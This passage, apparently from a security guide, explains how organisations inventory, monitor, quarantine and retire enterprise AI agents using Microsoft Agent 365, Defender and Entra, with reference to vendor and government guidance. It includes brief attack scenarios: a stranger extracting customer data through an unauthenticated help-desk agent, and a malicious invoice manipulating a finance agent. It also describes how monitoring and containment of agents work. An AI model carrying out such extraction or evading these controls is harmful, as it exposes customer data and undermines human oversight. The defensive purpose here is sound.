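Monitoring software can detect some of these events. Datadog's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Studio agent authentication modified* describes a rule that detects when someone changes an agent so that users no longer have to sign in. Datadog, which sells such software, classifies the change as an attack technique for keeping access to a system. An agent's maker might also remove the sign-in requirement for convenience, so the security team has to find out who made the change and why.

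In their March 2026 survey of attacks on agents, Dehghantanha and Homayoun recommend that organisations treat new instructions, policies and tools like any other change to live software, by assessing the risk, trying the change on a small scale and keeping a way to reverse it. They also suggest automatic tests that stop a change if the agent's unsafe action rate rises by more than two percentage points for any type of attack. This rate is the share of test scenarios in which the agent breaks a policy.

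That threshold needs more tests than the survey's example of 100 per attack type. Suppose an agent's true rate is 5% both before and after a harmless change. With 100 independent scenarios each time, the measured rate would rise by more than two percentage points about 20% of the time. With 1,000 scenarios, this would happen about 2% of the time.

### Building an inventory

Posture management is the continuing work of finding agents and correcting their weaknesses. It starts with an inventory, because an organisation can't recheck agents it doesn't know about.

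Microsoft's product for keeping published agents secure is Agent 365, which the company calls a "control plane for agents" (Microsoft, 2026). It went on general sale in May 2026. Microsoft says organisations had registered more than 50 million agents in it by 17 November. That averages about 250,000 a day, far too many for people to review one by one.

The 50 million figure doesn't show how many agents are in use or how many are secure. Microsoft's registry counts include agents from Microsoft and outside suppliers as well as those an organisation builds itself, so the total may include the same product many times.

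Agent 365 can also import agents from other companies' platforms. An administrator connects a platform once, and its agents appear in the registry with their owners and tools, without any change to their code. Microsoft lists both draft and published agents from Copilot Studio, and changes typically appear within 20 minutes. Draft agents from Agent Builder, SharePoint and Foundry (Microsoft's platform for developers) don't appear in the administrators' overview.

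Petri's *The Agents Entra Can't See* argues that the greater danger comes from agents that work through an employee's ordinary account on a trusted computer, because Microsoft's Entra identity service doesn't recognise them as agents. Agent 365 can discover some agents on employees' computers, but an organisation should still ask teams which agents they use and compare their answers with the registry.

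### Giving each agent an owner and an identity

The next step is to record who is responsible for the agent and which identity it uses. If the agent has its own Entra identity, administrators can distinguish it from a person in sign-in records and revoke its access separately. Microsoft also lets organisations limit how long an agent keeps its access and name a sponsor to oversee it.

A separate identity doesn't replace maker credentials, so someone still has to change the login of the help desk agent's database tool.

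After an agent changes owner, its tools may still depend on a former employee's account. According to Microsoft, when an administrator reassigns an agent, the new owner can edit and delete it and open files the previous owner uploaded, while the previous owner loses all access to it. Microsoft's instructions don't mention the logins that the agent's tools use, so the new owner should check them.

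### Checking settings and ranking risks

Microsoft Defender lets security teams search the settings of every agent registered in Agent 365. Microsoft provides ready-made queries and stores several snapshots of each agent over time. A security team can use the newest snapshot to find agents without authentication, and older ones to find out when somebody turned authentication off. These queries can find faults that appeared after the scan at publication.

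A large organisation will probably find more faults than it can fix at once. In a January post, Microsoft (2026) describes how Defender ranks agents by the harm an attacker could do:

- **Sensitive data.** Defender identifies agents connected to data such as customers' personal details.
- **Hidden instructions.** It looks for tools that read outside content alongside tools that could do damage. If such an agent also works with little supervision, Defender recommends adding human approval.
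- **Control over other agents.** A coordinator agent directs several others, so an attacker who takes it over may be able to misuse all of them.
- **A route in.** Defender maps attack paths, such as one that leads from an interface open to the internet, through an agent, to a store of confidential files.

By these criteria, the help desk agent should rank well above an unauthenticated agent that reads out the canteen menu. Microsoft doesn't explain in the post how Defender weighs the factors, so a security team should compare the ranking with its own knowledge of which data matters most.

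Entra also ranks agents by behaviour. It learns an agent's normal activity and flags departures from it, such as a jump in sign-ins, failed access attempts, or access to an unfamiliar resource. Microsoft classifies all these detections as offline, meaning they come too late to stop the action that triggered them.

Misuse of the help desk agent could easily go unnoticed, since a stranger's question leads to the same kind of database query as a colleague's. If the agent uses its maker's credentials, the query may not even appear under the agent's own identity.

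### Which features are available

Several of these features were still previews in late 2026, so Microsoft may change them before general release:

| Feature | Status |
|---|---|
| Agent 365 | Released in May 2026 |
| Blocking, deleting and reassigning agents | Documented without a preview label |
| Entra's detection of risky agents | Probably released |
| Defender's agent inventory | Preview in June 2026 |
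| Entra identities for agents from more platforms, including Google, Salesforce, OpenAI and Anthropic | Preview, with rollout due to finish in December 2026 |
| One continuously updated risk rating across Microsoft's products | Preview in November 2026 |
| Defender's posture assessment for Amazon Bedrock, Google Gemini, Google Vertex AI and Anthropic Claude agents | Preview in November 2026 |

The status of Entra's risk detection is inferred from a setup guide by the vendor AdminDroid, which mentions "preview versions" that customers may have configured earlier.

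In November, Microsoft presented posture assessment for other companies' platforms as an extension of Defender. An April version of Microsoft's documentation already listed Bedrock and Vertex AI in the preview inventory, so only Gemini and Claude seem to be new.

Microsoft gives every agent in Agent 365 a core set of security features but offers others only on supported platforms, so an agent listed in the inventory may not have full protection.

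### Repair, quarantine and retirement

Microsoft recommends that the security team ask the agent's owner whether a setting was intentional before changing it. The people who find a fault may not be the ones who fix it. In the Microsoft 365 admin center, for example, only two administrator roles can approve agents or assign owners, and other staff can only monitor.

If the agent could do harm in the meantime, an administrator can stop it in several ways:

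| Action | Effect | Main limit |
|---|---|---|
| Quarantine | Users and makers can still see the agent in Copilot Studio, but nobody can use it | Doesn't correct the fault |
| Block | Nobody in the organisation can use the agent in Microsoft 365 | For SharePoint and Foundry agents, affects only Copilot Chat |
| Disable the identity | The agent can't sign in to Entra or connected apps | Probably doesn't stop a tool that uses someone else's login |
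| Delete | Permanently removes the agent and its files | In the admin center, works only for Agent Builder agents |

Quarantine is usually the best first step for a Copilot Studio agent because an administrator can reverse it. Microsoft describes quarantine as a way to isolate an agent while administrators investigate and fix it.

Marking an agent as compromised in Entra raises its risk level to High, but blocks its access only if the organisation has already set up a policy for high-risk agents. An administrator who needs to stop the agent's sign-ins immediately should disable its identity.

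Microsoft is also adding ways to respond to a risky agent without shutting it down. In *Microsoft unveils tools to monitor and corral rogue AI agents*, Bishop (2026) reported in October that new features would be able to stop the agent from making changes or require a person to step in. The finance agent, for example, could keep answering questions about invoices while someone investigates a suspicious payment.

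Dehghantanha and Homayoun suggest emergency drills in which the security team starts a harmless incident, such as an agent stuck in a loop, and measures how long it takes to stop the agent. The team may discover, for example, that the only person with the right administrator role is on holiday.

Retirement needs more care than simply deleting the agent:

1. Put the agent on a list for retirement, limit who can use it and ask whether anyone still depends on it.
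2. Quarantine it for a while. If an important process stops working, restore the agent and find it an owner.
3. Export the logs and settings that the organisation needs to keep. Entra keeps risk detections for only 90 days, and deleting an Agent Builder agent also deletes its files.
4. Revoke the agent's credentials and close its connections. A stored key may still work after the agent has gone.
5. Delete the agent and confirm that it no longer responds. Deletion from the admin center can take up to 24 hours to reach every user.

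### A self-test at startup

Dehghantanha and Homayoun also propose a check that runs each time an agent starts. It would test whether the agent's policies have loaded and whether its input checks, sandbox, logging and limits on outgoing connections work. The system would then write a signed readiness record to the audit log.

The survey says the record should include a policy hash, the list of tools and the decoding parameters, which are settings such as how much randomness the model uses. A hash is a short fingerprint of a file that changes if anyone edits the file. Here is an invented record for the rebuilt help desk agent, with a start time and the test results added:

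```json
{
  "started": "2026-12-01T08:00:00Z",
  "policy_hash": "9f2c71",
  "tools": ["read_ticket", "find_customer", "send_email"],
  "decoding": {"temperature": 0.2},
  "tests": {
    "policy_loaded": true,
    "input_checks": true,
    "sandbox": true,
    "logging": true,
    "outgoing_limits": false
  },
  "signature": "b71e04"
}
```

This record contains two warnings. The limits on outgoing connections failed their test, and if the approved version had no email tool, somebody has added one since it was approved. The signature lets an investigator verify that nobody has altered the record. The survey recommends linking health checks to automatic quarantine or a restart, which would stop this agent before it served anyone.

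Testing a forbidden connection might have caught the wrong network setting in Anthropic's security tests. A record of that test would also supplement Google's signed builds, because it could cover settings someone chose after the build script signed the image.

The self-test would miss an insecure policy that loads correctly, a remote tool that keeps its name but changes its behaviour, and any change made while the agent is running. An organisation should also record the model's version, which isn't among the survey's three examples of what to record. A program separate from the agent should sign the record, because otherwise an attacker who controls the agent could sign a false one.

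The survey includes no test of how well this method works. The method requires control over how the agent starts, which customers don't have in a hosted product such as Copilot Studio. They can get part of the benefit by comparing each new inventory snapshot with the approved settings.

### From a blocked action to a new rule

Suppose a stranger finds the link to the original help desk agent in Copilot Studio. They ask what tools it has, and then ask for a list of every customer. Defender blocks the database call and raises an alert, as Microsoft describes. The organisation could follow the problem back to its cause like this:

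1. **Contain it.** An administrator quarantines the agent. Colleagues can't use it for now, but neither can the stranger.
2. **Find the setting.** An analyst opens the agent's inventory entry and finds that it has no authentication. The maker confirms that the database tool runs on maker credentials.
3. **Find out when it went wrong.** The snapshots show that authentication was already off when the maker first published the agent. The maker had seen the scan's warning and continued.
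4. **Look for earlier damage.** The analyst searches the logs for calls that Defender allowed. The stranger may have obtained several customers' details, one at a time, before asking for the full list.
5. **Correct the agent.** The maker turns on Microsoft sign-in, switches the tool to end-user credentials and publishes the agent again. The analyst repeats the stranger's questions without signing in, and the agent refuses to answer.
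6. **Change the rule.** An administrator uses a data policy to stop makers from publishing agents without authentication, an option that Microsoft documents. They test it by trying to publish an unauthenticated agent.
7. **Find similar agents.** The analyst runs the query for missing authentication across the organisation and asks each owner whether public access is intentional. The administrator releases the help desk agent from quarantine.

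The third step determines which rule to change. If the maker had turned authentication off months after publication, the organisation would also have needed an alert for that change, such as Datadog's. If the analyst had simply closed the alert after the block, the stranger could have returned with a less suspicious question.

Under the new rule, another maker could still publish an agent that requires sign-in but gives every colleague the maker's access. Restricting maker credentials would address this, but Microsoft notes that many organisations only block anonymous agents.

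### Should access or monitoring come first?

GitGuardian, which sells software for finding exposed credentials, argues that security teams should shift their effort from reacting to attacks to preventing them. When an agent uses a valid key to call a service it normally calls, each step looks legitimate, so a runtime detector may not have enough evidence to recognise an attack until after the agent has used the key. Removing the key beforehand prevents this misuse even if nobody recognises the attack.

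GitGuardian's best evidence is that more than 64% of the credentials it confirmed as valid in 2022 still worked when it tested them again in January 2026. It also found 24,008 different secrets in public MCP configuration files, of which 2,117 (about 9%) were valid.

GitGuardian reports that attackers took more than 10 valid credentials from over 44% of the developer laptops compromised in one malware campaign. Its text gives the figure for developer laptops in general, but the chart caption limits it to the compromised machines, so the figure doesn't show what an average developer's laptop contains.

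Microsoft places more emphasis on checks during execution. In its November announcement, it points out that agents often act with users' own permissions and argues that security teams need to be able to stop manipulated agents. For example, reducing stray credentials wouldn't protect the finance agent from a malicious invoice, because the agent needs its mailbox and payment tools to do its job.

Microsoft and GitGuardian both have a commercial interest in their answers, though Microsoft sells posture management as well as runtime protection. They also agree more than their difference in emphasis suggests. GitGuardian recommends runtime detection as a second layer, and some of its "pre-runtime" controls stop a running agent from reading or sending a secret.

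Reducing access should usually come first, because it limits the damage even from attacks that no detector catches. Reducing access would have solved most of the help desk agent's problem. After that, runtime checks matter most for agents like the finance agent, which needs dangerous permissions to do its job.

### What official guidance asks for

The non-profit OWASP publishes software security guidance, including a *Top 10 for Agentic Applications 2026*. According to GitGuardian, the listed risks include the misuse of legitimate tools, the abuse of identities and privileges, and compromised tools or MCP servers. A configuration review based on the list would therefore examine an agent's tools, permissions and suppliers, though using the list is voluntary.

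On 1 May 2026, the US cybersecurity agency CISA, the US National Security Agency and agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the UK released *Careful Adoption of Agentic AI Services* (CISA, 2026). TinyFish quotes its advice to assume that agents "may behave unexpectedly" and to prioritise resilience, reversibility and risk containment over efficiency. Narrow permissions and quarantine before deletion would fit that advice. The document is guidance, and the quoted passage uses "should" rather than "must". Reed Smith, a law firm, says the guidance focuses on systems in which several agents work together, so an organisation with single agents may have to adapt it.

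The US standards agency NIST is developing control overlays, which adapt its general catalogue of security controls to particular kinds of system. It proposes separate overlays for single agents and for groups of agents, and includes configuration settings among the components to protect. NIST's *Control Overlays for Securing AI Systems Concept Paper and Slack Channel* invites outsiders to contribute. NIST calls the overlays guidelines, so they don't bind a company on their own, though a customer could require them in a contract.

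### Who checks what, and what to keep

These measures fail if everyone assumes someone else is responsible for them. The division of responsibilities below would suit an organisation with a separate security team. In a smaller organisation, one person may fill several roles, but someone other than the maker should also review any agent that can reach sensitive data.

| Stage | Check | Person responsible | Evidence to keep |
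|---|---|---|---|
| Building | Whether the task needs each tool, permission and credential; scans of code and outside tools | Maker, within limits set by an administrator | The agent's purpose, owner, tools and permissions; scan results |
| Publication | Settings in combination; test attacks and ordinary tasks; compliance with publishing rules | A reviewer other than the maker | The approved version, test results, the decision and any exceptions |
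| Running | Changes since approval; runtime alerts; regular review of access and ownership | Owner for changes and reviews; security team for alerts | Settings snapshots, readiness records, tool calls, blocks and repairs |
| Retirement | Whether anyone depends on the agent; whether its credentials and connections still work | Owner, or an administrator if there is none | Exported logs, revoked credentials and confirmation of deletion |
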